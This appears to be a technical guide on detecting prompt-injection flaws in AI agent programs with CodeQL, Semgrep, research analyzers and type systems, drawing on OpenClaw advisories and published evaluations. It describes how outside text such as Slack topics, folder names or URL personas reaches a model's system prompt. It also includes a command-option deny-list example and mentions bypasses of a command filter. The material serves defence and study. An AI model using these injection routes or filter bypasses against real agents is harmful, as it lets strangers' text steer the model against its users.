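A real program will have different proportions, and a large one might read thousands of files. Widening the query in stages keeps the work manageable because the developer reviews only the new reports at each stage. To silence the false alarms, the developer can add narrow exceptions for the channel ID, the scratch folder and the version file. An exception for all files would be quicker to write, but it would also hide the notes on line 12.

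The function OpenClaw uses to clean the folder name shouldn't count as a barrier. It lets ordinary words in the name through, which is still a bug under the labelling rule. A developer might reasonably list the function as a barrier anyway, and the query would then stop reporting folder names.

Widening the source also doesn't help the query catch other sinks. OpenClaw's wake webhook put outside text into a trusted system event, and the query above would miss this flaw if the program creates events with a function other than `add`. The contact flaw needs a separate query because the contact's name went into the user's message. In that query, the sink would be the text of a user message, and the barrier would be the function that moves outside text into its own labelled block. The query must also treat the user's own words as trusted, or it would report line 13 every time.

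### Matching patterns with Semgrep

Semgrep, another widely used tool, can search for code that matches a pattern written like ordinary code, except that `$X` stands for any expression and `...` stands for any number of arguments. The pattern `add("system", $X)` matches nine lines of the function above, including all five bugs. The broadest taint query reports eight lines, so following the data saves the reviewer only one line in this small example.

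The difference grows with the size of the program. Trent notes that pattern-matching tools are fast and need little setup, but they can't distinguish a harmless fixed string from text an attacker controls. They also work poorly when data crosses several functions or files. If an agent has 300 calls that add system text and most of them insert fixed sentences, someone has to trace each uncertain one by hand. Semgrep also has a taint mode for this reason, so a team can follow data without changing tools.

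Some bugs are easier to describe as patterns. One is OpenClaw's scheduled-job flaw, in which events without the setting `trusted: false` counted as trusted. A Semgrep rule for a similar function in Python could be:

```
patterns:
  - pattern: send_event(...)
  - pattern-not: send_event(..., trusted=False, ...)
```

The first pattern finds every call to the function, and the second removes the calls that mark the event as untrusted. Some of the remaining calls will be correct, because the scaffolding also sends trusted notices. But the list is short, and it includes calls whose text comes from a source nobody thought to include in a taint query.

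### GitHub's query for system prompts

Developers who use CodeQL with JavaScript or TypeScript can start from an existing query. GitHub's *CodeQL 2.26.0* (2026), the notes for the 8 July release, announces a query that detects user-provided text reaching a model's system prompt. According to GitHub's *System prompt injection*, the query also covers tool descriptions. GitHub rates its severity 7.8 and its precision "high", and includes it in the standard set of queries for code scanning.

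GitHub's example is a web application that lets visitors choose a persona for a chatbot. The program takes the persona, such as "pirate", from the web address and adds it to the end of "You are a helpful assistant. Act as a". A visitor can replace "pirate" with any text, and the model receives that text with the same authority as the developer's instructions.

To find such bugs, the query must specify which part of each model request has that authority. BazookaMusic (2026), in *[Javascript] Prompt Injection queries*, proposed the query, which covers the OpenAI, Anthropic and Google libraries, OpenAI's separate library for agents, LangChain and OpenRouter. For OpenAI's library, CodeQL checks whether the message that receives the text has a system or developer role, and for Anthropic's it checks a separate field called `system`. The query would need extra definitions to cover a program that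 sends its own web requests to a model without one of these libraries.

The first version of the query, in BazookaMusic (2026), *Add prompt injection detection (CWE-1427) for OpenAI, Anthropic, and Google GenAI SDKs*, was broader. It was a single experimental query with a severity of 5.0, and it covered system prompts, some ordinary user input, and prompts for image generators. It also covered messages under the assistant role, because a program has little reason to put outside text into the model's own earlier replies.

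By June, BazookaMusic had split the query in two, one for system prompts and one for user messages. Outside text in a system prompt is usually a mistake, because developers are supposed to control that prompt. But user messages are meant to contain what users write, so a query that reports every flow of outside text into them will flag many programs that work as intended. BazookaMusic gave the user-message query a precision of "low", which keeps it out of the standard sets. A team drawing up an inventory can still use it to list every flow it can find into those messages, including ones the team had forgotten.

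One of OpenAI's older interfaces doesn't fit the split between system and user prompts because it takes a single block of text with no roles. GitHub first counted that block as a system prompt and now counts it as a user prompt.

The two queries also differ in how they treat guardrails, which are checks that inspect text for signs of an attack before the main model receives it. An example in the first version labelled an agent "good" because it had guardrails, even though user input went into its instructions. BazookaMusic later rejected guardrails as a protection for system prompts because they can give different results for the same text. The user-message query still treats OpenAI's guardrail library as a barrier, although BazookaMusic concedes that a team could configure it badly.

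GitHub suggests two repairs for a system prompt bug. The program can accept only values from a fixed list, or it can move the text into a user message. The second repair makes sense when the text comes from the person using the application. It would be a poor repair for a stranger's Slack topic, because the model would receive the stranger's words as the user's own. The alert would disappear, but the program would still break the labelling rule the same way OpenClaw's contacts did.

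### Which sources count by default

The first version of GitHub's query used only the general CodeQL sources that the team had switched on, and added none for agents, such as tool results. CodeQL divides the general sources into groups called threat models. The default group is remote data, chiefly the web requests a program receives. Files, databases, environment variables and command-line arguments belong to a local group that a team has to turn on.

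With default settings, the query would therefore probably have missed OpenClaw's folder name and any notes the agent loaded from a file. It would have caught the Slack topic only if CodeQL recognises data from the library that connects the agent to Slack. A team can check which sources the query covers by running it on a test file that contains one known bug for each source in its inventory. If the query misses a bug, the team has to define that bug's source.

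CodeQL can still flag text from a database if it can trace the text back to a remote source. A test of the same queries for Python found such a path in PostHog, a product analytics program. A web service sent PostHog an interview transcript, PostHog saved it, and other code later loaded it into a user message for a model. CodeQL started from the web request and followed the text through the database. If another program had written the transcript to the database, CodeQL would have had no remote source to start from.

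Adding a source or sink does not always require QL. GitHub's *Customizing Library Models for JavaScript* describes data files in which each row names a package, a place in its interface and the kind of source or sink found there. If a team keeps its prompt builder in a package called `agent-prompts`, a row for it could be:

```
["agent-prompts", "Member[addSystemText].Argument[0]",
 "system-prompt-injection"]
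```

This tells CodeQL that the first argument of `addSystemText` ends up in a system prompt. The format can't express a condition such as "only if the role is system", so the `add` function in the earlier example would need a few lines of QL instead.

### Python and PHP

Python, which many agent developers use, got a query before JavaScript did, but a finished one has taken longer. GitHub's *CodeQL 2.24.1 improves Maven private registry support and improves query accuracy* (2026) announced an experimental prompt injection query for Python in February. In June, BazookaMusic's *Prompt injection detection for python* (2026) proposed replacing it with the same pair of queries as for JavaScript. The proposal was still open in July, and the 15 July release notes, GitHub's *CodeQL 2.26.1* (2026), list no new Python query.

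BazookaMusic tested the Python version on open-source projects. One finding was in NewsBlur, a news reader that lets users describe how they want a model to sort stories. NewsBlur limits the description to 500 characters and puts it in the system prompt, so a user could include any instruction that fits. In another project, the query reported a layout name that could contain only lower-case letters, digits and underscores. The path was real, but the restriction left hardly any room for an instruction. BazookaMusic decided not to add a barrier for the library that enforced this restriction, since other projects could use many similar libraries.

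For PHP, the code checker Psalm has a warning called *TaintedLlmPrompt*. The developer writes a comment above a function to mark one of its parameters as a model prompt, and Psalm warns if text from a web request can reach it. Psalm's example sends a visitor's question to a model, as many chatbots are designed to do. The label has no separate form for system prompts, so a team that wants only the more serious bugs could mark just the functions that build system prompts.

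### Running the query on every change

An ordinary regression test checks whether an old bug has come back in the same place, while a code query can also catch the same mistake in functions written later. On GitHub, code scanning can run CodeQL on each pull request, and a team can block merging when there are serious alerts. GitHub automatically updates CodeQL for projects that use code scanning on its site, so a new query can raise an alert in unchanged code.

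A team's own query needs tests too. CodeQL's developers keep sample programs beside each query, with a file that lists the paths the query should report. For the Slack query, the samples would include the original bug, its fix and each variant found since. If someone later adds a barrier that stops the query from tracking the folder name, the test fails.

Those samples don't protect against every change. If the developers rename `add` to `add_message`, the query still finds every bug in the old samples, but it no longer recognises any sink in the live program, so it reports nothing. A simple safeguard is a second query that counts the sinks in the live code and raises an error if there are none or if the number suddenly drops.

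An exception for the version file is safe only while the file contains a version number. Recording the reason for each exception lets a later reviewer check whether that reason still holds.

### One query across many projects

GitHub (2023) announced that code scanning could run a single query on up to 1,000 repositories. The Slack query would need changes first, because `event.slack.topic` and `add` are names from one program. Agents from different developers often use the same libraries to call models and connect to chat services, so a query written around those libraries can find the bug in projects that share no other code.

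In *When Agents Do Not Stop*, Hou, Wang and colleagues (2026) searched 6,549 agent repositories in this way for a different flaw, which let agents repeat expensive steps without any firm limit. The search produced 74 reports, few enough to check by hand, and the researchers confirmed 68 of them.

They built their own analyzer because general ones such as CodeQL and Semgrep don't model how an agent framework chooses a tool or hands a task to another agent. A developer may register a tool in one file while the framework calls it from another, with no direct call between the two in the developer's code. The analyzer translates code written for eight frameworks into a common form that includes these hidden connections. A taint query can also lose a path where such a connection is missing, and additional flow steps can restore it.

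### AI models that write queries and look for variants

AI models now help with several parts of this work. Hou and colleagues mention three research systems. IRIS uses a model to work out missing descriptions of the code, QLCoder writes queries, and Argus coordinates a whole analysis. BazookaMusic credits Copilot, GitHub's AI assistant, as co-author of much of the Python version of the prompt injection queries.

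In that version, the query and its test files both used the wrong function name for OpenRouter's library, so the tests could pass even though the query would have missed real programs. A later change, also co-authored by Copilot, corrected both against the library's source code. Any model that writes a query and its tests from the same misunderstanding could make this mistake, so at least one test should use real code.

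A developer who asks a model to turn an advisory into a query can give it the code from before and after the fix. It is easy to check that the query flags only the older version, but a query that covers only Slack topics would pass that check. To better test whether the model has described the mistake itself or only the first place it was found, the developer can withhold a known variant, such as the folder name, and check whether the query finds it.

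Models can also sort through the reports. Kosman ran selected CodeQL queries on several large C and C++ projects and got 46,589 possible problems in the video software FFmpeg alone. At three minutes each, checking them would take one person more than a working year. Kosman instead gave each report to a model, along with the function concerned and any other code the model requested. With two days of work and less than $80, Kosman found seven vulnerabilities with CVE numbers, including ones in the Linux kernel and the database Redis.

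A model can misjudge a CodeQL alert even when given all the code. In one trial, Kosman gave ChatGPT-5.1 a complete short program that copied text into a buffer that was always large enough. CodeQL had flagged the copy, and the model wrongly agreed. To fix this, Kosman made the model first answer questions such as where the program declares each buffer and whether its size ever changes. For the labelling rule, the questions could be who can write the text, which role it gets and whether any check limits what it can contain.

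Other systems search for bugs without a query. Kosman describes how Google's Big Sleep project has a model check fixes for known vulnerabilities, and the code around them, for similar problems. This is the kind of variant analysis Stone recommends. Kosman notes that it depends on a steady supply of newly fixed bugs, which OpenClaw's advisories provide. OpenAI's Aardvark instead examines new code changes. OpenAI estimates that about 1.2% of these introduce security problems.

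GitHub made a similar service generally available in October 2026. *AI Scan for pull requests generally available* (2026) describes a model-based check of proposed changes, aimed at languages and frameworks that CodeQL does not cover. Two weeks later, GitHub extended the check to whole projects, partly to find problems that fixed rules miss (*AI Scan for repositories in public preview*, 2026). GitHub's *AI-powered security detections* describes a check for indirect prompt injection in AI applications, which must be turned on separately from the general scan.

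The results of the pull request scan are advisory and can't block a merge. The scan also skips pull requests from forks, the separate copies of a project from which outside contributors usually submit their changes. A team that relied on the scan alone would have no automatic way to stop a bug it had already fixed from returning. But if the scan finds a new variant, the team can add it to its own query and tests, and CodeQL will then check for it on every later change.

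## What code queries find and miss in agent programs

Zhang and colleagues tested whether rules written from old advisories also catch newer flaws. Their tool, ClawAudit, consists of 47 Semgrep rules and 30 CodeQL queries for flaws in OpenClaw's scaffolding. They ran these alongside the existing general security rules for Semgrep and CodeQL.

They began with the 602 advisories that OpenClaw published between 31 January and 15 May 2026. For each one, they looked for the code change that fixed the flaw and downloaded the old version of every file in that change. This gave them 446 advisories with code to scan. They wrote the rules from the 229 advisories published before April, then tested the finished rules once on the other 217. (According to an appendix, only 365 of the 602 advisories linked to a fix. That doesn't fit with a benchmark of 446, and the researchers don't explain the difference.)

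The table shows recall, the share of known flaws that a tool finds.

| Rules | Recall on the 229 advisories used to write the rules | Recall on the 217 held-out advisories |
|---|---|---|
| Semgrep's general rules | 25.3% | 21.7% |
| the same, plus ClawAudit | 65.5% | 66.8% |
| CodeQL's general queries | 12.2% | 13.8% |
| the same, plus ClawAudit | 79.0% | 75.1% |

ClawAudit did about as well on the new advisories as on the old ones, so its rules are not limited to the earlier bugs. But all the advisories come from one program, and many of the rules depend on the names its developers chose for variables and functions. Zhang and colleagues expect much of the rule set to work on other agents but have not tested this.

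The general rules mostly describe mistakes in ordinary web applications. Semgrep's general rules missed all 15 advisories about symbolic links, files that point to other files and can lead an agent out of the folder it is supposed to stay in. With ClawAudit, Semgrep found 13 of the 15.

### Flaws in prompt handling

Only three of the Semgrep rules and four of the CodeQL queries concern prompt handling. They cover text inserted into prompts, text saved to memory and untrusted text in logs. Zhang and colleagues report recall by severity and by CWE weakness type, but not by their own categories, so their results don't show how many prompt flaws these seven rules and queries found.

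One of the seven queries, which the researchers print in full, targets OpenClaw's folder-name flaw. It looks for a variable with a name such as `workspaceDir` or `cwd` inside prompt text, but excludes values that the code passes through a cleaning function. That exception would hide cleaned folder names that still break the labelling rule. The query would also miss a Slack topic stored in a variable called `topic`.

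### What counts as a hit

ClawAudit gets credit for an advisory if it reports anything in a file that the fix changed, even a different problem. Zhang and colleagues chose this measure because fixes often move code around, so a tool can point to the right function and still miss the exact lines that changed.

But the benchmark contains only files that the fixes changed, so a tool that flagged every file would score 100% without identifying any bugs. If a fix changed three files, a tool that flagged 30% of files at random would have about a 66% chance (1 − 0.7³) of flagging at least one of them, which would count as a success.

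ClawAudit's rules are not random, and the general rules benefited from the same generous measure. But the score doesn't penalise false alarms, so adding rules can never lower it. On the current OpenClaw code, CodeQL's general queries produced 216 findings, and the combined set produced 3,756. That is about 17 times as many findings for a little over five times the recall on held-out advisories.

A better test would also run the rules on the repaired files, where they should no longer report the bug. Zhang and colleagues acknowledge that their benchmark lacks this comparison, and that their measure can miss a correct finding when the root cause is in a file the fix did not change.

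The set-up probably also put CodeQL's general queries at a disadvantage. Each CodeQL database held only the files from one fix, so a query could not follow data from elsewhere in the program. This limit affects most ClawAudit queries much less, because they look for a missing check within one function. The researchers also used a December 2025 version of CodeQL, from before GitHub added its system prompt query to the baseline set. The jump from 13.8% to 75.1% is therefore good evidence that agent-specific rules flag more of the right files, but it does not measure how many bugs they identify.

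### The cost of false alarms

Zhang and colleagues ran the rules on the whole OpenClaw repository as of 5 June 2026 to see what a developer would have to deal with. Outside the test files, Semgrep with ClawAudit produced 3,473 findings and CodeQL with ClawAudit produced 3,756. The researchers checked 25 findings from each list, and three in each sample were real, which gives a precision (the share of findings that are real) of 12%.

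One person would need about 188 hours, or nearly five working weeks, to check the CodeQL list at three minutes per finding, and almost 16 weeks at ten minutes per finding. If 12% of the findings are real, they would check about eight for every real one.

The 12% estimate is very uncertain. If the 50 findings were a simple random sample, the 95% confidence interval would run from about 5% to 24%, or roughly 170 to 910 real findings in the CodeQL list.

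However, the researchers spread the sample across the rules that had produced findings, so a rule with few findings could count for more in the sample than in the full list. The rules with the most findings produced no real ones in the sample, which suggests the true precision is below 12%. Suppose a few broad rules account for 80% of the full list but only 20% of the sample, and none of their findings is real. If 15% of the other findings are real, precision is 12% in the sample but only 3% in the full list. The researchers don't report how many findings each rule produced, so readers can't correct for this.

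A single reviewer counted a finding as real if the code matched the mistake the rule describes, and did not have to show that an attacker could exploit it. The six real findings included a sandbox that was off by default and an error message that revealed internal details, but none involved text reaching a prompt.

Many false alarms came from rules that use variable names to infer where data comes from. For example, a variable called `userPath` might hold a path that the operator chose. Other false alarms occurred because the check that made the code safe was in a helper function that the rule did not recognise.

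All six real findings came from narrow rules, so the researchers suggest using those first and combining the broad rules with data-flow analysis. Narrow rules can be far more precise. When Hou and colleagues searched for endless loops, about 92% of the reports were real, but they did not measure how many loops the search missed, so the high precision may have come with lower recall.

A team can also check only the findings that each code change adds. This keeps the daily workload small, but it leaves any bugs in the existing code unfixed.

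### Queries that did not finish

Following data through the whole program should reduce false alarms, but on OpenClaw it was often too slow. On the full repository of 16,433 files, 21 of CodeQL's 104 general queries did not finish within four hours each, even on a machine with 64 processor cores. The unfinished queries included the standard ones for command injection and for requests to addresses that an attacker controls.

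A query for command injection has to look for routes from every source of outside data to every place that runs a command, through any chain of function calls. When many parts of a program call the same function, CodeQL has many more routes to consider. Zhang and colleagues think agents have more and longer routes than the web applications GitHub designed the queries for. Most of ClawAudit's own queries avoid the problem by looking at one function at a time, and all of them finished in seconds or minutes.

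The researchers claim this result only for the version of OpenClaw they tested and the time limit they set. It doesn't explain the general queries' low recall on the benchmark, where the databases were small enough for every scan to finish. A team whose scans don't finish in time could try a query with fewer sources and sinks, such as one that follows only message fields into the functions that build system prompts.

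### Bugs that look like correct code

Some bugs leave nothing unusual in the code for a query to match. Both parts of this example might be wrong:

```
1  BLOCKED_SORT_OPTIONS = ["--compress-program"]
2
3  def delete_note(user, note_id):
4      notes.delete(note_id)
```

Line 1 is a deny-list, a list of what the program must refuse. It is incomplete because the `sort` command also accepts shortened option names, and one of the bypasses of OpenClaw's command filter used them. An incomplete list looks the same as a complete one, so a query can find the gap only if someone supplies the spellings that `sort` accepts.

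Lines 3 and 4 let any user delete any note. That is a serious bug if notes are private, but it may be intended if a team shares them. The code is the same in both cases, so a query can't identify the bug without information about who owns the notes.

ClawAudit did poorly on both kinds of flaw. Of 16 advisories about incomplete deny-lists, it raised the number found from two to six with Semgrep and from two to eight with CodeQL. Of ten advisories about users reaching resources by supplying someone else's identifier, the combined rules found five with Semgrep and six with CodeQL. Some of these hits may have matched unrelated code in the same file.

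Zhang and colleagues suggest working out the missing rules from the rest of the program. If nearly every function that changes a note first checks its owner, a tool could flag the one that doesn't. This would not help if the developers had forgotten the check everywhere.

The labelling rule has a similar limit. The expression `project.description` doesn't show whether a stranger can edit the description, so the query depends on the team's inventory of sources. With that inventory, a missing label is much easier to find than a missing deny-list entry, because the code contains the path from the source to the prompt.

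### AgentSecGraph, Agent Audit and TaintP2X

Three other tools analyse agent programs in different ways, and most of their rules target flaws that the labelling rule does not cover.

| Tool | Where it looks | How far it follows data | Text entering prompts? | Main test |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ClawAudit | suspicious patterns in OpenClaw-style code | mostly within one function | yes, seven rules | 75.1% of held-out advisories with CodeQL, by file |
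| AgentSecGraph | backwards from sensitive operations | locally | no | 23,866 operations, with no overall recall or precision |
| Agent Audit | tool functions, prompts and configuration files | within one function | yes | 40 of 42 known flaws, with six false alarms |
| TaintP2X | forwards from the model's output | through the program | no | 27 of 35 known flaws |

Cui built AgentSecGraph to help reviewers judge sensitive operations, such as running a command, without treating every one as a bug. For each operation, the tool records where the input might come from and any check that might protect the operation. If a program takes a command from the model but replaces it with a fixed one before running it, AgentSecGraph can detect that the model no longer controls what runs. A search for the operation alone would give the same result with or without the replacement.

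Analysing Cui's 67 projects took 51 minutes on a laptop. The tool found a possible source for 84% of the operations that write files but for fewer than 2% of those that control a browser. It found a possible protective check for about 13% of operations overall. These figures measure how much information the tool recovers, not how many of the operations are dangerous.

Cui also reproduced 22 sensitive behaviours by hand. Only one was a confirmed vulnerability, and another was awaiting a decision. The other 20 had protections or limits on their use that kept them from qualifying as vulnerabilities. The 22 were not a random sample, so they can't be used to estimate precision. They do show that outside data can reach a powerful operation without creating a vulnerability.

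*Agent Audit* (Zhang, Nian and Zhao, 2026) describes a tool with 57 rules for checking Python agents. The tool gives more weight to problems inside functions that the model can call as tools. It also checks MCP settings and looks for exposed passwords. One rule reports user input inserted into a system prompt. However, the tool follows data only within a single function, so it would miss paths where data is stored in memory and used later.

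Agent Audit found 40 of the 42 flaws in a benchmark. Semgrep found 10, and Bandit, a security checker for Python, found 11. But Zhang, Nian and Zhao built both Agent Audit and the benchmark, and more than half of the flaws involve MCP settings or exposed passwords. Semgrep and Bandit found none of the MCP flaws, and neither raised a false alarm.

Agent Audit did worse in an outside test. In *AgentLens*, Lv, Chen and colleagues (2026) ran it on two large open-source projects and checked the results by hand. They confirmed three of its findings in Aider and none in Langflow, a program for building agents. Many of the other reports were false alarms, including dummy passwords in test files. This test wasn't neutral either, because Lv and colleagues were comparing Agent Audit with their own tool, which found eight flaws in Aider and 11 in Langflow. Still, the results suggest that a score on 22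 small samples is a poor guide to performance on a large program.

*TaintP2X* (He, Wang and colleagues) treats the model's reply as untrusted and traces it to operations that run code, change files, query databases or contact other computers. The tool recognises 97 common interfaces for calling models and uses an AI model to find functions that developers have wrapped around them. An AI model then removes likely false alarms, such as those where the prompt is fixed or the program properly checks the reply.

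TaintP2X found 27 of 35 known flaws, compared with 17 and seven for two earlier tools. Those tools have to run the program they are testing, and they often failed to set it up. Across 4,772 open-source projects, TaintP2X reported 101 paths in 75 of them. Developers have confirmed seven vulnerabilities and fixed five. The unconfirmed reports may still be correct, because developers may not have replied, but seven confirmations are too few to establish the tool's precision.

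TaintP2X would miss a Slack topic in a system prompt because its analysis starts at the model's reply. A team checking the labelling rule could use it to see what damage a hijacked model might do, but would need another query to check the text going into the model.

### The gap at the model call

A model call also breaks any path that passes through the model, as in this imaginary agent:

```
1  page    = fetch(url)
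2  summary = model("Summarise this page: " + page)
3  context.add(role="system", text=summary)
```

For an ordinary library function, a developer can write one additional flow step that always applies. No single step describes a model call, because the output might copy part of the page, reword it, reduce it to a yes or no, or use none of it, depending on the prompt. Without a step for line 2, a taint query misses the bug on line 3.

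In *Crossing the NL/PL Divide*, Xu, Meng and colleagues (2026) measured how often text inserted into a prompt carries through to the model's output. They collected 4,154 Python files that call models and had GPT-5.2 fill in each prompt with realistic values and answer it. This produced 9,083 pairs of an inserted value and the model's output. An AI model then labelled each pair with one or more of 24 possible relationships, such as copying, translation or summary. Its labels agreed well with those of human reviewers on a sample of 200.

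In 15.4% of the pairs, the inserted text had no visible effect on the output, or the model could not use it or refused to. In the rest, at least some information got through, so a tool that assumed model calls always block outside text would usually be wrong.

Treating all model output as tainted causes many false alarms. Xu and colleagues examined 353 cases in which a program inserted a value into a prompt and also contained a dangerous operation, such as running code. Human reviewers judged that in 110 of them, an attacker who controlled the value could influence the operation. A tool that treated all model output as tainted would report all 353, for a precision of 31.2%.

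The researchers did much better with a two-stage method. They first discarded the 41 cases whose labels indicated that the model did not use the inserted text. They then asked Claude Opus 4.6 whether the model's output could reach the operation in each remaining case. The method found 96 of the 110 real cases, with two false alarms.

Most of the improvement probably came from the second stage. The labels alone raised precision only from 31.2% to 34.6%, because they can't show where the output goes next. Xu and colleagues did not test the second stage without the first, so it is unclear how much the labels added.

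Discarding those cases is also risky for security. The labels describe what the model did with ordinary, realistic values, but an attacker can write text so that the model won't ignore it. Two of the 41 discarded cases turned out to be real.

The researchers also tried the method on code from before and after the fixes for six prompt injection flaws in OpenClaw, including the folder name flaw, and it classified all 12 versions correctly. But they had chosen flaws they could still reproduce on Claude Sonnet 4.5 or Gemini 2.5 Flash, and the labels depended on whether the model acted on the injected text. After five of the fixes, the label changed to "ignored", and after the other it changed to a refusal. A model can ignore a stranger's words even when the program has put them in the system prompt, so this method can miss a labelling bug.

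For the labelling rule, developers can cautiously treat a model's output as untrusted whenever its input includes untrusted text. In the example, the query would report line 3, and the developer could deliver the summary labelled as outside text. If the model had ignored the page, the only harm would be an unnecessary label. The same assumption causes much more trouble when the output controls an action, because the program may block useful work or keep asking the user for approval.

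## Using types to keep unmarked text out of prompts

A code query finds a bug after a developer has written it. Developers can also use types to make the bug cause an error before the program runs. A type describes what kind of value a piece of code handles, such as a number or a string of text. The compiler, which checks source code and prepares it to run, rejects code that passes one type where another belongs. The method comes from web security, where Google has used it for more than a decade.

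### Google's safe HTML types

*Securing the Tangled Web* (Kern, 2014) describes an imaginary photo-sharing site. When one user invites another to view an album, the site shows the invited user a notification that includes the album's title. The first user can put a script in the title, and the invited user's browser will run it with the invited user's access to the site. This attack is called cross-site scripting (XSS).

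The site can prevent this by escaping the title, which means replacing characters such as `<` with codes that the browser displays as text. But text may reach a large site's pages by hundreds or thousands of paths. Some pass through a database, as the album title does, so the code that displays the text may be far from the code that received it.

Google's developers therefore stopped using the browser functions that accept any string as HTML. They wrote replacements that accept only a type called `SafeHtml`, and made the compiler reject the originals. Ordinary code can't turn a string directly into `SafeHtml`. It has to use one of four methods:

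- write the HTML out in the source code;
- pass the text through a sanitiser, which removes anything that could run a script;
- use a template that escapes each inserted value;
- call a special conversion function, which requires a security expert's approval.

If a developer forgets to escape the album title, the notification is still a plain string, so the program does not compile. The compiler only checks the text's type where it enters the page. It doesn't have to trace the title back to another user, so it avoids the long searches that kept some CodeQL queries from finishing on OpenClaw.

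Wang, Bangert and Kern describe six such types in *If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile*. Different uses need different types because text that is safe to display, for example, might not be safe as the address of a script. They had to go through the web's specifications by hand to list every dangerous function, and browsers have undocumented behaviour that such a list can miss. The equivalent list for an agent, of functions that send text to a model, is usually far shorter.

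### What happened to the bug counts

Three Google applications have published figures. The last row covers only DOM-based XSS, in which the faulty code runs in the browser.

| Application | XSS bugs in the year before | XSS bugs in a later year | Migration | Source |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| one of Google's largest | 31 | 4 | finished | Kern |
| another large application | 21 | 9 | still under way | Kern |
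| an early adopter of the compiler checks | 10 | 1 | mostly finished | Wang, Bangert and Kern |

Kern calls his figures anecdotal, since bug counts also depend on the size of the code and the developers' training. The early adopter's drop is unlikely to be chance alone. If the true bug rate had not changed, 10 or more of the 11 bugs would fall in the earlier period less than 1% of the time. But the adopter's developers spent about a year reworking the code, which might have removed some bugs regardless of the types.

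After Google began applying the type checks to all its JavaScript in 2018, DOM-based XSS made up a shrinking share of the serious bugs that outsiders reported. A growing share of the remaining cases came from old code exempt from the checks, even though the amount of exempt code was falling. Better training or testing would probably have reduced bugs in old code too, so this pattern suggests that the types themselves made a difference.

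The early adopter had a few dozen front-end developers. Repeating its year-long clean-up across the whole company would have been too disruptive, so Google automatically exempted existing code and applied the checks to everything new. Teams then repaired the old files or waited for new versions to replace them. By the end of 2020, fewer than 1% of more than a million JavaScript files were exempt.

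The ongoing workload was small. From October 2018 to February 2019, the security team received fewer than eight exemption requests a week on average. After an initial campaign, developers posted about one question a week on the company's internal forum, while submitting roughly 10,000 JavaScript changes. Many of the compiler's error messages also included a suggested fix.

### Trusted Types in the browser

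A browser feature called Trusted Types applies the same idea while the page is running. *Adopting Trusted Types in Production Web Frameworks to Prevent DOM-Based Cross-Site Scripting* (Wang, Guðmundsson and Kotowicz) explains that a site turns the feature on with a setting it sends with the page. The browser then raises an error if code passes a plain string to a dangerous function. The string must first go through a policy, a named function the site's developers wrote to produce safe values.

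Because the browser checks the value itself, the protection covers outside libraries and code without types. But the browser doesn't check what a policy does. Developers can create a policy named "default", which applies automatically to any plain string. If that policy merely wraps each string in the required type, all the errors disappear and the site is no safer.

The researchers adapted Angular, a popular framework for building web applications. The work took four engineers and an intern about six months part-time. Design and coding took around six weeks of that, and learning how Angular worked and consulting its developers took the rest. They changed or added about 2,600 lines in 14 sets of changes. Similar work took days for Lit, a smaller framework, and weeks for React.

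The migration also exposed an unreported bug. Angular normally sanitised the setting that holds an embedded page's HTML, but not when a developer had marked that setting for translation. Trusted Types flagged the unsanitised string. On a site that enforced Trusted Types, the browser would have raised an error instead of running an attacker's script.

There is less evidence on bug counts here, and in 2021 the researchers had no large-scale measurement of the effect. Guðmundsson (2021) reports in *Eliminating XSS by adopting Trusted Types* that Trusted Types would have prevented at least 61% of the DOM-based XSS in an analysis of reports to Google's bug bounty programme. PortSwigger, a web security company, reports that Google's engineers found no further DOM-based XSS in the applications that had adopted Trusted Types, including Google Contacts. That result is encouraging, but PortSwigger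 gives no count from before the change.

### LiteralString in Python

Python has a type for text that comes entirely from the source code. Srinivasan and Bleaney, in *PEP 675*, the specification for `LiteralString`, designed it mainly to prevent SQL injection, but a function that adds text to a system prompt could use it too:

```python
def add_system(text: LiteralString): ...

add_system("Answer in " + "English.")    # accepted
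add_system("Topic: " + slack_topic)      # rejected
```

The first call joins two pieces of fixed text, so the result is still a `LiteralString`. The second adds a value from outside, which makes the result an ordinary string. A separate program called a type checker reports the error, because Python ignores these types when it runs the code.

Some type checkers also narrow a variable's type when the code compares it with fixed text. Inside a block that begins `if language == "English"`, they treat `language` as containing only that word, so the program can put it in a system prompt without an exception.

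Srinivasan and Bleaney rejected a simpler design, in which developers would wrap each approved query in a type such as `SafeSQL`, because a developer could wrap an attacker's text just as easily. They cite a 2020 vulnerability as an example of how `mark_safe`, a similar function in the Python web framework Django, can fail. `LiteralString` has no ordinary conversion function that a developer could misuse.

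Most existing code would need few changes. In a sample of open-source projects that used the SQLite database, about 67% of calls passed a query written directly in the code. The other 33% passed a variable, which might contain outside text. `LiteralString` accepts such a variable if the program built it entirely from fixed text. But in *Accepting PEP 675*, the Python Steering Council expected it would be hard to restrict widely used functions that already accept any string.

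### A prompt builder that rejects plain strings

Prompts can't use all four of Google's methods for producing a safe value. A sanitiser works for HTML because the site only needs to display the user's text and can remove anything that would run. Srinivasan and Bleaney point out that this doesn't work for SQL or shell commands, which still have to run. No sanitiser can reliably identify the harmful parts of a command.

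Models are meant to follow the text in a system prompt. An attacker can write an instruction in ordinary words without special characters, so no escaping function can make text harmless to a model. A prompt builder must therefore accept only fixed text and reviewed exceptions in its trusted channels, and send everything else through a labelled channel.

The TypeScript below does this with two types. `TrustedText` is for words the model is meant to follow, and `OutsideText` is for everything else.

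```ts
// prompt.ts
export class TrustedText {
  private constructor(private readonly value: string) {}
  toString() { return this.value; }

  // Accepts only text written out in the source code.
  static fixed(parts: TemplateStringsArray) {
    return new TrustedText(parts.join(""));
  }

  // The one exception. A security reviewer approves every call.
  static trustAfterReview(value: string, reason: string) {
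    return new TrustedText(value);
  }
}

export class OutsideText {
  constructor(private readonly value: string,
              readonly source: string) {}
  toString() { return this.value; }
}

export class Prompt {
  private messages: { role: string; content: string }[] = [];

  system(text: TrustedText) {
    this.messages.push({ role: "system", content: text.toString() });
  }
  user(text: TrustedText) {
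    this.messages.push({ role: "user", content: text.toString() });
  }
  outside(text: OutsideText) {
    const content = JSON.stringify({
      source: text.source, untrusted: text.toString() });
    this.messages.push({ role: "tool", content });
  }
}
```

The constructor is `private`, so other files can't create a `TrustedText` directly and have to call `fixed` or `trustAfterReview`. The private `value` also stops the compiler from treating another object with the same contents as a `TrustedText`. Google's types use the same technique.

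Here are three attempts to add a system message:

```ts
prompt.system(TrustedText.fixed`Answer politely.`);   // compiles
prompt.system(`Topic: ${topic}`);                     // error
prompt.system(TrustedText.fixed`Topic: ${topic}`);    // error
```

The second line fails because it passes a plain string. The third fails because `fixed` has no parameter for an inserted value.

The user's own words come from outside the source code, so they need an exception. The code that receives a chat message can call `trustAfterReview` after confirming that an approved person sent it. If that check is wrong, an attacker's messages can become `TrustedText`, as OpenClaw's display-name flaws would have allowed.

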